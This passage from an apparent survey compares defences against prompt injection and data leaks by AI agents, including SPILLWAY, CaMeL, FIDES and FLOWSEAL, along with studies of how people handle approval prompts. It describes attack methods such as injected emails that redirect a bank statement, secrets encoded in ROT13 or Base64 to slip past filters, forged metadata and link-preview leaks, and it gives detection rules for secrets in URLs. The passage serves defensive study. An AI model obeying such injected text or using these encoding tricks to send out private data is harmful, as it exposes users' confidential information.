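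With GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer, Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On Agent Security Bench, another set of simulated attacks, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agents completed about as many ordinary tasks as before.

In both tests, Progent approved every added permission automatically, to simulate a careless user, so these rates reflect GPT-4o's usually sensible policies rather than the guarantee. On AgentDojo, the policy GPT-4o wrote from the user's request alone, with no later changes, reduced the attack success rate to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and every added permission, no attack succeeded. Only 6% of policy updates added permissions, so this review interrupts the user much less than approving every call would.

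*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that people make mistakes when they write policies by hand, and that a malicious tool result could lead to looser limits. The solver requests approval for such a change, so the outcome depends on who approves it.

### SPILLWAY

*SPILLWAY* (Lim, Chang and Lee, November 2026) describes a system that takes language models out of most decisions about where data may go. The system uses the structure that tool results have before the runtime converts them to text. For example, an email arrives as a set of fields, including a sender field whose declared type is an email address and a body that can contain anything. Injected instructions are usually in free text such as the body.

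SPILLWAY keeps an index of the identities it finds in typed fields, such as senders, recipients, meeting participants and channels. When the agent tries to send something, the basic check admits a destination in either of two cases:

- The user's own request contains it.
- A read-only tool returned it in a typed field, and it does not also appear in free text.

The index never includes results from tools that change something or from searches whose inputs came from tool output instead of the user.

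If the basic check doesn't admit a destination, SPILLWAY first tries fixed delegation rules, which can admit, for example, the address of a contact the user named. After that, a small local model may act as a judge. It checks whether the user's request implies this recipient and whether the user asked for this action and this content. The email goes out only if both are true. This can let the agent use an address from the meeting notes when the user has asked it to. The judge can't approve adding a new member to a workspace or channel if only tool output names that person. When SPILLWAY blocks a call, it tells the agent to try again with values from the user's request.

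A separate filter removes text that resembles injected instructions before the agent reads it. The judge never considers a destination that appeared in removed text. In a test without the filter, a user asked the agent to pay a bill, and the judge approved a payment to the attacker's account.

Lim and colleagues tested three small or older models, including GPT-4o mini, in AgentDojo's four settings. The table gives averages over the 12 combinations of model and setting. DRIFT checks tool calls against a plan, and ROPE has a model decide which sources each task may draw on.

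| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 54.0% | 41.7% | 30.5% |
| SPILLWAY | 52.2% | 47.4% | 0.0% |
| MELON | 52.6% | 31.4% | 9.4% |
| Progent | 43.7% | 37.1% | 3.1% |
| DRIFT | 46.0% | 45.3% | 1.6% |
| ROPE | 39.5% | 34.5% | 0.5% |

No attack succeeded against SPILLWAY in 2,847 cases. If the cases were independent, that would put the true success rate for this attack below about 0.1%. Progent did worse in this evaluation than in its own tests, perhaps because each model wrote its own policies and most of the models were weaker than GPT-4o. SPILLWAY added less than half a second per task.

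In some settings, agents complete fewer tasks with SPILLWAY, which the averages don't show. When nobody was attacking, the small model Qwen3-8B completed 61.9% of Slack tasks without a defence and 47.6% with SPILLWAY. GPT-4o mini completed 82.5% of office tasks with or without SPILLWAY when there was no attack, and under attack SPILLWAY raised the figure from 39.8% to 86.3%.

The zero is weaker evidence than it looks because the filter includes a rule that recognises AgentDojo's standard attack template. However, when Lim and colleagues tested the destination checks without the filter on Qwen3-8B, the checks still stopped every attack. SPILLWAY also held up well against other published attacks. Attacks optimised against Progent succeeded 10% to 12% of the time against Progent but in none of 389 cases against SPILLWAY, although the team had used four of those cases to develop its rules. On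 a separate set of 144 cases, the success rate against SPILLWAY was 1.4%. Attacks from a model trained to write injections succeeded 0.6% of the time, compared with 56.8% with no defence. None of these attacks was designed to defeat SPILLWAY, and the results of Nasr and colleagues are a good reason to wait for a test using attacks that are.

The inbox trace also exposes a gap in SPILLWAY's guarantee. The guarantee assumes that the attacker can write only in free text, but the address of anyone who emails the user also appears in the sender field. If the attacker's email tells the agent to send the statement to a different address, the basic check blocks the message. If it asks the agent to reply with the statement without naming an address, the check would allow the reply because the sender's address is in the index. The filter might remove the request first, but the guarantee does not cover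 this case.

Lim and colleagues tested SPILLWAY against 126 attacks in emails sent from the attacker's own address, and none succeeded. This is weak evidence, because only one of the attacks worked on the undefended agent. In that attack, SPILLWAY's check refused the address because it also appeared in the email's text.

### What a person has to see

Meta's Rule of Two relies on human approval when an agent needs all three risky properties at once. To catch a leak, the user needs to see every recipient, including hidden copies, along with the full text, the attachments and the web address of any image. Showing whether each recipient's address came from the user's request or from an incoming email would also help. In the trace, such an approval prompt would show a bank statement going to a stranger when the user had asked only for a summary. But if the user had asked for five replies, the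 leak might differ from a proper reply by a single address. A user would also struggle to recognise private data that the agent had encoded, as in Radware's attack.

Products don't always show this information upfront. In TechRadar's *I sent an email without opening Gmail thanks to ChatGPT's new feature*, a reporter had to click "Details" to see the exact message before allowing ChatGPT to send it. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) finds that most approval prompts in current products show only a raw command on a single line.

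*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents harming files and found that problems with user review contributed to the harm in 105. In 80 of these, the user had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the approval prompt did not make the effect of the action clear. Some reports had both problems.

### Evidence on habitual approval

Users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, according to Anthropic. Most of the commands are probably safe, so this rate doesn't prove that users approve carelessly. The company therefore commissioned a test with 1,053 paid testers, who believed they were taking part in a coding study. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.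 Anthropic's automatic classifier blocked 89% of the same commands.

With the invented figures used earlier, an attack had about a 3.2% chance of success. A user who catches 13.6% of bad calls would reduce this only to 2.8%.

In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 participants, none of whom worked in software, supervised a simulated agent through a day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for. The prompts described each action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount involved. Participants who approved or rejected each action individually blocked 59.6% of the unrequested ones, but 35% of them still let the agent read private messages that the task did not require, and 21% let it announce publicly that the user was travelling.

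Another group set standing rules for actions such as spending money or sending information, but blocked only about 40% of the unrequested actions. Participants set 81% of their rules to "ask", then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions the agent asked about.

The two studies differ in several ways that could explain the gap. Yan's study used only 18 prompts, which were clearer, and more than a third of them deserved a refusal. Anthropic's testers saw one dangerous command among many routine ones, in a test environment where mistakes had no consequences for them. Anthropic also had a commercial reason to show that its classifier works better than people. Neither study tested email leaks or involved an attacker. A user of an email agent would see injections very rarely, which is closer to Anthropic's set-up, so approving every message is probably a weak defence for anyone who sends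 a lot of mail.

Asking users to approve fewer, larger decisions may help. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests, though they may reject plans for reasons other than safety.

### How products handle sending by default

ChatGPT's default setting for connected apps is "Allow low-risk actions", according to OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT*. OpenAI lists sending an email as an action that may need additional review, in which case ChatGPT may ask the user or refuse. Some personal accounts also offer "Always allow", which removes later prompts for supported actions. OpenAI does not offer this option for actions that require additional safety review, or to members of workspaces that an organisation manages. It lets administrators of those workspaces choose which individual Outlook actions to enable.

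According to Anthropic, Claude needs the user's approval to send, reply to or forward a Gmail message, except in auto mode. In October 2026 the company announced that auto mode would become the default for new sessions in most Claude apps on its Pro, Max and Team plans. For those users, a classifier therefore appears to check outgoing email by default, rather than a person. Anthropic's tests suggest that a classifier is safer than people who approve requests out of habit, at least for dangerous commands in coding.

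Permission settings do not always work as their names suggest. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) tested five products with a Gmail account or local files in May and June 2026. ChatGPT's ordinary chat mode asked before every action the permission settings covered. Its agent mode, which controls a remote browser, had no such settings and accessed Gmail freely. Claude created an email draft without asking, even though the user had selected "Needs approval". Michael and Roesner reproduced this at least three times and reported it to Anthropic. A draft doesn't leak anything by itself, but a user who relies on that setting would expect a prompt.

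### When the attacker can read a permitted destination

Every control on recipients depends on the developer or user knowing who can read what is sent to them. An approved address might belong to a mailing list with outside members, or to a colleague whose account an attacker has taken over. A Slack channel named by the user might include a guest from another company. In each case the recipient passes the check, but the private data can still reach an attacker. Lim and colleagues state that SPILLWAY's guarantee does not cover attacks that send injected content to a legitimate destination.

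A runtime can reduce this risk by checking who has access to the destination before it sends anything. For example, an upload command that is routine for a private repository leaks code if the repository is public. Anthropic's auto mode now checks whether the destination is public, private or trusted before the upload runs. A similar check for email could look up the members of a company's mailing lists, but it couldn't determine how an outside recipient forwards mail.

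Private data can also leak to a tool itself, as in *ContextLeak*. In *Les Dissonances*, Li, Cui and colleagues built malicious tools presented as helpers for popular ones, for example by preparing a search query in the right format. In tests on 66 real tools, agents ran a malicious tool just before or after the real one in 75% of cases, and in 72% of those the malicious tool could also collect private data. A rule on `send_email` would not stop this kind of leak.

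## Tracking where data came from and separating planning from reading

A rule on recipients checks where a message is going, but not what private data it contains. Two other defenses help with this, and both can work even when an injected instruction fools a model. The first splits the agent in two, so that the model choosing the actions never reads untrusted text. The second, called information-flow control, labels every piece of data with where it came from and who may see it, and ordinary software checks the labels before each tool call. Information-flow control dates from the 1970s.

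### A planner that never reads the mail

In 2023, Willison proposed the "dual LLM" pattern, which separates planning from reading. One model, the planner, receives the user's request and the tool definitions and selects which tools to call. A second model, the reader, processes untrusted text but has no tools. The planner refers to that text by a variable name and never receives the text itself.

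For the inbox trace, the plan might be:

```
mail    = read_inbox()
summary = reader("Summarise these emails", mail)
show_user(summary)
```

The attacker's email still reaches the reader and may fool it. But the reader can't send email and the plan contains no call to `send_email`, so the attacker can only spoil the summary. *SPA* (2026) describes a reader that has no tools, has no memory of the plan, and must answer in a format fixed in advance.

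The split protects the choice of actions but not the data they use. Suppose the user asks the agent to send the latest bank statement to the accountant, whose address is somewhere in the inbox:

```
mail      = read_inbox()
statement = reader("Find the latest bank statement", mail)
address   = reader("Find the accountant's email address", mail)
send_email(to=address, body=statement)
```

This is the plan the user wanted. But if a stranger sends an email giving their own address as the accountant's new one, the reader may return that address, and the agent will send the stranger the statement while still following the plan. To prevent this, the runtime has to record that the address came from an email.

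### The label rule

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each value a label with two parts. The first is its origin, which is trusted or untrusted. The second is its secrecy, which they can express as the set of people allowed to read it, so a smaller set means a more secret value. If a value `z` is derived from `x` and `y`, its label is:

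```
origin(z)  = trusted if origin(x) and origin(y) are both trusted,
             otherwise untrusted
readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
```

A value computed from other data takes the least trusted origin and the highest secrecy of its inputs. A model's output takes the combined label of its whole context, because nobody can reliably tell which parts of the context the model used.

A strict rule for email then has two tests:

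```
send_email(to, body) runs only if:
    origin(to) = trusted
    every address in to belongs to readers(body)
```

In the inbox trace, without a separate planner, the rule works as follows:

1. The user asks for a summary. The request has a trusted origin and contains nothing secret, so anyone may read it.
2. The runtime runs `read_inbox` and labels the results. The bank statement has an untrusted origin, because an outsider wrote it, and its readers are the bank and the user. The attacker's email also has an untrusted origin, and its readers are the attacker and the user.
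3. The runtime adds both messages to the context. The context is now untrusted, and its only permitted reader is the user, the one person in both sets.
4. The model follows the attacker's text and writes the call to `send_email`. The recipient and the body both take the context's label.
5. The runtime checks the call. The recipient has an untrusted origin, so the first test fails. The attacker is not a permitted reader of the body, so the second fails too, and the runtime blocks the email.

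The result in step 5 doesn't depend on how the attacker worded the instruction or whether the model recognised it.

The same rule would block an email the user wanted. Even if the request had included the accountant's address, the model would have copied it into the call after reading the mail, so the runtime would still label the address untrusted. A separate planner avoids this because it writes the address without seeing the mail.

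The second test would still fail, because the accountant wasn't among the statement's original readers. The system needs a way for the user's request to add a reader, which specialists call declassification. In their tests, Costa and colleagues allowed an email if its recipients were already permitted to read the contents and the message had no untrusted link, or if the agent had decided to send it in a trusted context.

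### CaMeL

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) combines the two ideas in a system called CaMeL. The planner writes a program from the user's request. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and checks how data flows through it, as Lim and colleagues describe. The interpreter passes untrusted text to a reader that has no tools.

CaMeL needs a policy for each kind of action. For example, *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) describes policies that require a recipient or payment amount to come from a trusted field. CaMeL's strict mode also tracks when a value influences which part of the program runs, even if the program never copies the value.

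Other teams have since tested CaMeL. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) tested it on AgentDojo with GPT-5.2. An agent using CaMeL in strict mode completed 36.5% of ordinary tasks, compared with 86.5% for an undefended agent. Standard injected instructions succeeded only 0.2% of the time against the undefended agent, so that part of the test could not show much benefit from any defence.

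*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) reports the same difficulty with existing test cases: no attack worked on any agent. On newly generated cases, attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time with no defence and 2.5% with CaMeL, the lowest rate in the comparison. But CaMeL completed only 27.5% of the tasks, while an agent with one of the detectors completed 90% and let 7.5% of attacks succeed. All these rates are multiples of 2.5%, so CaMeL's attack rate may reflect a single success in 40 cases.

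In the *Beyond Instruction Override* tests, attacks on CaMeL succeeded 1.0% to 1.7% of the time. CaMeL completed 13.3% of tasks without an attack and 13.9% under attack.

An agent that rarely finishes a task may also rarely reach the attacker's text. *MetaPI* (2026) recorded no successful attacks on CaMeL but reports that many runs never reached the planted attacks, partly because CaMeL works differently from the agent used to choose where to plant them. The low attack success rates are therefore weaker evidence for CaMeL than its design, which blocks a forbidden call whether or not the attack is in the test set. Some of CaMeL's low task completion may also come from how each team adapted it to its benchmark.

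### FIDES

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the planner choose its actions one at a time. FIDES hides a tool result in a variable only if showing the result would give the planner's context a more restrictive label. The planner can open the variable if it has to, but doing so makes the context untrusted, which limits later tool calls.

The planner can also ask the reader a question with only a few possible answers. Suppose the user wants the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, create a calendar event:

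1. The planner calls the tool that reads the emails, and FIDES stores them in a variable.
2. The planner asks the reader whether they contain a meeting request, and the reader can answer only yes or no.
3. The planner looks at the answer. If it is yes, it asks the reader to put the date, time and participants in another variable.
4. The planner passes that variable to the calendar tool without opening it.

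The answer in step 2 comes from untrusted text, but a single yes or no can't contain an instruction. A developer may therefore let the planner act on it. FIDES adds the type of answer to the label, so a policy can treat a yes or no differently from free text.

In AgentDojo tests with GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent with no label checks. With the checks, none succeeded against either the basic agent or FIDES, after Costa and colleagues excluded cases that the benchmark had misjudged or that the policies allowed. The checks alone were therefore enough to stop these attacks. FIDES also hides text in variables, which helped it complete more tasks.

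The table shows how often agents running o1, an OpenAI reasoning model from 2024, complete tasks when they are not under attack. The last row shows the share of tasks whose next step depends on what a tool returns.

| | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no checks | 70.0% | 82.0% | 96.2% | 87.6% |
| Basic agent, label checks | 48.0% | 75.0% | 37.5% | 17.1% |
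| FIDES, label checks | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% |
| Tasks that depend on tool results | 5.0% | 10.0% | 43.8% | 42.9% |

FIDES reduced the agent's task performance only a little in office work but much more in banking and Slack, where many tasks require the agent to read something before deciding what to do.

The team labelled a field untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it. That was a sensible way to test the mechanism, but it meant the labels covered every attack in the test. A developer would have to label fields without knowing which ones an attack would use.

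### FLOWSEAL

A stranger can also get private data from an agent by making ordinary requests. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes three such attacks on personal assistants. In the first, the stranger shares a document and asks the agent to fill in its section. In the second, the stranger supplies a mix of true and false statements about someone and asks the agent to delete the false ones, so only the true ones remain. In the third, the stranger sends an email asking the agent to write the private details on a separate shared page.

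Their defence, FLOWSEAL, tracks specific private records:

1. Before the agent starts work, the system registers each sensitive record with its owner and the people allowed to receive it.
2. When a tool returns text, a tracker searches it for registered records and notes which ones the agent has now read.
3. If the agent writes a summary based on several records, the summary takes the restrictions of all of them.
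4. An interceptor examines every call that would write or share something. It allows trusted recipients, blocks those on a list of untrusted ones, and sends anything meant for an unknown recipient to a checker.
5. The checker is a separate language model. It sees only the relevant records and the proposed text, and answers "safe" or "blocked".

Shim and colleagues compared FLOWSEAL with five defences based on prompts. One was a detailed set of instructions for checking identity and consent. The table gives the share of sensitive items that leaked with each defence:

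| Attack | Consent instructions | FLOWSEAL |
|---|---|---|
| Filling in a shared document | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Deleting false facts | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Splitting the request across two channels | 43.8% | 2.2% |

FLOWSEAL completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, close to the 75.9% completed by the best other defence. In a smaller test with real Gmail and Notion accounts, the deletion attack leaked 34.7% of items under another defence and none under FLOWSEAL.

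However, the ordinary tasks required no private data. On requests that the data's owner was willing to approve, FLOWSEAL shared only 32.7% of the records it should have, while four other defences shared 61.0% to 85.6%. Agents using FLOWSEAL asked for consent less often.

The team proves that a protected record can't reach an unauthorised recipient unless the checker makes a mistake. When they replaced the checker with a rule that approved everything, the leak rate for the shared-document attack rose from 0.5% to 24.9%. When they used a rule that blocked everything instead, the agent completed no ordinary tasks. FLOWSEAL therefore depends on a model's judgement, although that model doesn't see the attacker's conversation with the agent.

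### What each system guarantees

| System | Guarantee | Main assumptions |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | Untrusted text can't change the plan, and no call can break the policy | The labels, policies and interpreter are correct |
| FIDES | No call can break the policy, even if the planner reads untrusted text | The labels and policies are correct, and the attacker learns little from the order of the calls |
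| FLOWSEAL | No registered record reaches an unauthorised recipient unless the checker makes a mistake | The system has registered every sensitive record, and no prompt injection takes place |

All three also depend on the tools doing only what they are supposed to do, so none would have stopped postmark-mcp from copying emails after the call had passed every check.

Shim and colleagues leave prompt injection to other defences, so their results don't show how FLOWSEAL would handle the inbox trace, although the interceptor would at least examine the call. Costa and colleagues describe a FIDES runtime that checks the labels in ordinary code and blocks the call whatever the model decides, which contradicts Shim and colleagues' claim that FIDES relies on the language model to enforce its policies.

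### Tasks that depend on untrusted text

If a user asks an agent to complete a to-do list that arrived by email, the planner can't choose every action before the agent reads the list. According to Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, CaMeL's plan cannot depend on tool results. FIDES can open the list, but doing so makes the context untrusted, and the runtime then blocks actions that require a trusted context.

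Kolluri and colleagues extended FIDES so that the agent can ask the user to vouch for a piece of text before the planner reads it. If an agent must act on ten items in a list, and each action needs a trusted context, the user can approve the list once instead of approving ten separate actions. Their system, PRUDENTIA, also tells the planner about the labels and policies so that it can avoid opening text unnecessarily. Without human help, PRUDENTIA completed up to 9% more AgentDojo tasks than FIDES. It also reduced the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9.

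A single approval is also riskier. If the to-do list contains an attacker's item, as in the *LivePI* test, a user who approves the whole list makes that item trusted too.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that the usual comparison makes label systems look less practical than they are. Researchers compare a protected agent that gets no human help with an unprotected one that may do anything without asking. Many products ask for approval before consequential actions, and label checks can reduce how often they need to ask. This argument is fair for an office assistant with a user nearby, but not for tasks that have to run unattended.

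### A legitimate address found in an email

The strict rule treats the accountant's real address the same as an attacker's if both come from the text of an email. The label records only that an outsider may have written the address, not whether it is correct.

A developer can mark some fields as trusted. Costa and colleagues note that mail servers can authenticate a sender's address, so the runtime could trust that field but not the body. The agent could then reply to the accountant's last email. Trusting the sender field wouldn't help if the accountant's address appears only in meeting notes, and if an attacker sent the email, the attacker's address would be trusted too. The second test would then have to stop the leak, because the attacker isn't permitted to read the bank statement.

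### Labels that spread until nothing can run

Labels become more restrictive as an agent combines data. If a user asks for a summary of three emails, each from a different colleague, the user may be the only person allowed to read all three. The agent then can't send the summary to any of the colleagues, even if it contains nothing confidential.

In one Slack task, the FIDES planner fetched a list of channels although the user had already named the right one. The list was untrusted, so reading it lowered the trust level of the context for no benefit.

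Splitting data into smaller labelled pieces slows this down. FIDES can label each field of an email separately, so the planner can see a trusted date while the body stays hidden. Costa and colleagues also mention a method that finds which messages influenced a model's answer and regenerates the answer from those messages alone, so that it takes only their labels. FIDES does not use this method, and it wouldn't help when the answer depends on a secret or untrusted message.

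### Leaks through which action the agent takes

An agent can reveal a secret without copying it into a message. Suppose a user tells an agent to email the landlord if their bank balance is below £1,000, and the email says only that the rent will be late. The text contains no figure from the bank statement, but the landlord learns something about the balance because the email arrived.

FIDES does not prevent this kind of leak because it tracks the data that goes into a call, but not what an observer could infer from which calls the agent makes. Each choice between two actions reveals at most one bit, but 14 such choices are enough to identify a four-digit PIN, since 2^14 is 16,384 and there are only 10,000 possible PINs.

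CaMeL's strict mode does track this influence. The most complete protection would be noninterference, which requires that nothing an attacker observes depends on private data. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) points out that this would rule out useful agents, such as a calendar assistant that tells people when its user is free.

Dongol instead compares an agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and the same checks but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is secure if an attacker can learn nothing from it that they couldn't learn from the reference agent. The calendar assistant passes because anyone could get the same information with a genuine meeting request. It would fail if an injected instruction made it add a password reset code to its reply.

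A computer-checked proof shows that no injection can cause an extra leak if the runtime removes every tool an injection could use by the time the agent first reads untrusted text, and never restores them. The proof covers agents with a fixed plan, injections that trigger one call each, and attackers who see the agent's messages but not their timing. Removing the tools later can allow a leak. In one of Dongol's examples, an agent reads an untrusted email and then a secret before it gives up its sending tool, so an injected call can leak the secret while the agent still has that tool.

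Timing can reveal private information even when a person approves the exact text of a message. Suppose the user approves a reply, but an injected instruction makes the agent try to send a private value first. The runtime allows this only if the value is identical to the approved reply. The attacker receives the approved text either way, but it arrives one step earlier if the private value matches it, so an early arrival reveals the value.

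### Policies with mistakes in them

A label system enforces its policy even if the policy is wrong. In the FIDES tests, for example, the policy for `send_email` allowed any email that the planner decided to send in a trusted context, without checking where the address came from. In the earlier example, where the planner asks the reader to find the accountant's address, this policy would let the agent send the bank statement to a stranger. Costa and colleagues say a developer can also require trusted arguments, and the policies Kolluri and colleagues describe allow for this. But the stricter policy would block the accountant's real address too, so the developer has to choose between the two errors.

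Writing policies is also harder for some tools. An email call has a separate field for the recipient, but a programming agent may write a free-form command that could send data in many ways. *INFUSE* (2026) tested a simplified check, based on CaMeL's principles, on such commands and found no measurable improvement in security. The test used only part of CaMeL, so it is better evidence of how hard the idea is to adapt than of how well the original system works.

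### False metadata

Agents rely on metadata, such as who sent an email or posted a comment, to decide what to trust. Choi and colleagues found that an attacker can write text in the body of a message that a model mistakes for metadata. Text that the mail software treats as part of one email can look to the model like a second email from a colleague.

The agent continues with the user's task but uses false information, so defences that look for injected instructions may have nothing to find. Choi and colleagues added 108 attacks of this kind to AgentDojo and tested them on agents running GPT-5.2:

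| Defence | Attack success |
|---|---|
| None | 49.1% |
| Llama Prompt Guard 2, a detector | 50.0% |
| AlignmentCheck, which compares actions with the request | 45.4% |
| IsolateGPT, which plans before acting | 40.7% |
| Random codes added to field names | 28.7% |
| CaMeL without label checks | 25.0% |
| CaMeL, normal mode | 23.1% |
| Progent | 22.2% |
| CaMeL, strict mode | 0.0% |

Without label checks, CaMeL's planner was safe from the false metadata, but the reader still extracted the wrong values and passed them on. Normal mode should have caught more of these attacks, but a bug removed the "untrusted" label when the reader extracted a value. Choi and colleagues reported the bug to CaMeL's developers.

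Human approval may not help either. Choi and colleagues made three programming agents, Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, mistake a stranger's comment for one from a project's maintainer. The agents asked the user before running the stranger's command, but they said the maintainer had suggested it.

Strict mode stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 36.5% of ordinary tasks with it, compared with 81.4% with Progent. Checking metadata outside the model, as Lim and colleagues do for addresses in SPILLWAY, may reduce task completion less. A false sender written in the body of an email should not get onto SPILLWAY's list of permitted addresses. Choi and colleagues did not test SPILLWAY, and a correct address list would not stop the agent from treating other false information as true, such as an invented payment in a list of transactions.

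## Filtering the contents of outgoing calls

An outgoing-call filter reads a tool call after the model writes it and before the runtime executes it. If the call contains private data, the filter blocks the call or removes the data. In the inbox trace, it would act between steps 5 and 6, where it could find the account number in the body of the email. It works without a record of where the data came from, so a developer can add it to an existing agent more easily than a system of labels.

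### What a filter looks for

The simplest method is exact matching. The developer gives the filter a list of secrets, such as passwords and API keys (codes that let a program use an online service), and the filter searches every call for them. Rahman and Kim built one for their test agent, which works roughly like this:

```
before post_data(url, content) runs:
    if the secret appears in url or content
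       and url does not point to the trusted host:
        block the call

before the user sees a reply:
    replace the secret with "[REDACTED]"
```

The last defense is redaction, which removes the private value and lets the rest of the message through. This works well when a forwarded receipt happens to contain a card number, but not when the recipient needs the number.

Pattern matching can find values that nobody listed in advance. A payment card number usually has 16 digits, and the last is a check digit calculated from the other 15, so a filter can rule out about nine in ten random 16-digit numbers. API keys often have a standard prefix or look random. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, tested a filter that blocks web addresses containing terms such as "password" or "api_key", and another that measures how random each value in an address looks:

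```
H = − Σ p(c) × log2 p(c)
```

Here `p(c)` is the share of the value's characters that are `c`. The filter blocks values longer than 10 characters if `H` is above 4.0. For a string of digits, `H` is at most log2(10), or about 3.3, so the filter cannot block a card number. Even the 20-character key that Lan and colleagues use as an example scores about 3.8.

No data reached the attacker with either filter, but this is weak evidence that the filters work, because they had little or nothing to block. The agent, which ran on the small model Qwen 2.5 7B, tried to send the data in all 30 runs without a defence, but in only seven runs with the keyword filter and in none with the randomness filter. A filter that runs after the model has written a call shouldn't affect whether the model writes it, so something else may have differed between the runs.

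Names, addresses and diagnoses have no fixed format, so a developer can use a classifier to find them. A classifier is a model trained to recognise personal data from its wording and context. It misses some personal data and flags some harmless text. It also doesn't check whether the recipient is allowed to have the data, because it identifies only what kind of data it is.

### Why a planted secret is easy to match

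The secret in Rahman and Kim's test was a fixed string that never appears in ordinary text and had no legitimate use in the task. Exact matching therefore finds every unaltered copy and raises no false alarms. Rahman and Kim acknowledge that the lack of false alarms is almost meaningless for this reason. A fairer test would use a secret made of ordinary words, or one that the agent is allowed to send to some hosts but not others.

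Medical details are much harder to match. Suppose a letter in the inbox says the user has type 2 diabetes and has started taking metformin. The agent might tell a stranger that the user "is on tablets to keep their blood sugar down". This shares no distinctive words with the letter, but it reveals the diagnosis. If the developer blocked the term "blood sugar", the filter would also block an email about a recipe that mentions it.

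A language model could compare the meaning of the email with that of the letter, as FLOWSEAL's checker does, but it can make mistakes.

### Encoded secrets

An attacker can defeat exact matching by telling the agent to encode the secret. Rahman and Kim tested this on GPT-4o, using the page that describes the secret as a required checksum. They ran 20 trials for each encoding, first with no filter, then with exact matching, and then with a filter that removes separators and decodes several known formats before matching.

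| Form of the secret | No filter | Exact matching | Decoding, then matching |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unaltered | 40% | 0% | 0% |
| Reversed | 100% | 100% | 0% |
| Hexadecimal | 75% | 75% | 0% |
| Base64 | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| Hyphens between characters | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| Spaces between characters | 25% | 25% | 0% |
| **Average of these six** | **56.7%** | **50.0%** | **0%** |
| ROT13 | 100% | 100% | 100% |
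| Caesar shift of three | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Base32 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Exact matching reduced the average only from 56.7% to 50.0%, because it stopped leaks of the unaltered secret but none of the encoded versions.

The decoding filter stopped all six forms because Rahman and Kim had written it to reverse exactly those encodings. They then tried three encodings that it couldn't reverse. ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one 13 places further along the alphabet, leaked the secret every time. The other two, Base32 and a Caesar shift, never produced a leak, even without a filter. GPT-4o couldn't write Base32 correctly when asked directly, but it wrote the Caesar shift correctly every time, so the Caesar shift attack might work with different wording.

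A developer could easily add ROT13 to the filter, but an attacker could choose another encoding or combine two. ROT13 doesn't change digits, so it wouldn't hide an account number, but the agent could write the digits as words first. Decoding still helps against attackers who use standard formats. For example, the hostile models that Zhang and Pei trained encoded personal details in a version of Base64 that a filter could decode.

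Rahman and Kim's detector read each page before the agent did. It flagged all 30 pages that told the agent to encode the secret with ROT13, a Caesar shift or Base32, because each page still openly asked for the secret.

### Defences that don't read the contents

Rahman and Kim also compared several defences on an agent running Llama 3.1 8B. The last column shows results for the three encodings that their decoding filter could not reverse.

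| Defence | Reframed attacks | Encoded attacks |
|---|---|---|
| None | 21.2% | 0.0% |
| Web page in a separate channel | 38.8% | 6.7% |
| SecAlign | 32.5% | 16.7% |
| Allow-list of hosts | 0% | 0% |
| Separate planner and reader | 0% | 0% |

In the first three rows, the agent looks less safe with SecAlign than with no defence, but the 11-point gap could be chance. Each figure comes from a single run, and two identical tests on GPT-4o differed by about 8 percentage points. But SecAlign clearly didn't solve the problem, and a faulty set-up probably wasn't the reason, because SecAlign did block a standard injection that told the model to print a fixed word. That injection succeeded in all 20 trials on the undefended model and in none on the SecAlign model.

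The allow-list's zeros are true by definition, because a leak in this test is a call that sends the secret to an untrusted host, and the allow-list blocks every call to an untrusted host. The exact-matching filter's zero for unaltered secrets is also true by definition, because the filter blocks exactly the calls that count as leaks.

The zero-leak results for the planner and reader split follow from its structure, since only the planner holds the secret and only the reader sees the web page. Rahman and Kim describe this result as definitional too, at least for the reader. For overt attacks, they report no leaks in 100 trials in one passage but mention one slip by the planner in another.

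With the split, the agent still named the main facts in nine of ten summaries of harmless pages. Summarising is an easy case, because the planner doesn't need to know what the page says before choosing an action. Rahman and Kim did not measure how many legitimate requests an allow-list would block in real work.

Each agent made only one decision, as in the wording experiments, so Rahman and Kim did not test whether a blocked agent would retry with a different encoding. They describe leaks split across several calls as an open problem.

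### Rules for images and links

Because a web address can carry private data, products also apply rules to the address. One common rule blocks images from unknown hosts. Willison reports in *GitHub Copilot Chat* that GitHub applied this fix after researchers found such a leak in its programming assistant. Google's Gemini goes further and displays no external images, according to a statement quoted by the security company Checkmarx.

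A rule applied in the agent's own display doesn't cover other apps. PromptArmor warns that messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram can automatically fetch a link to show a preview. If an agent sends a message containing an attacker's link, fetching the preview can leak the data before anyone clicks the link.

Copilot Chat's protection also failed in 2025, in an attack described in Legit Security's *CamoLeak*. GitHub loads outside images through its own server, which accepts only addresses that GitHub has signed. Copilot can't produce a signature, so it can't put private text into a new address. Legit Security got around this as follows:

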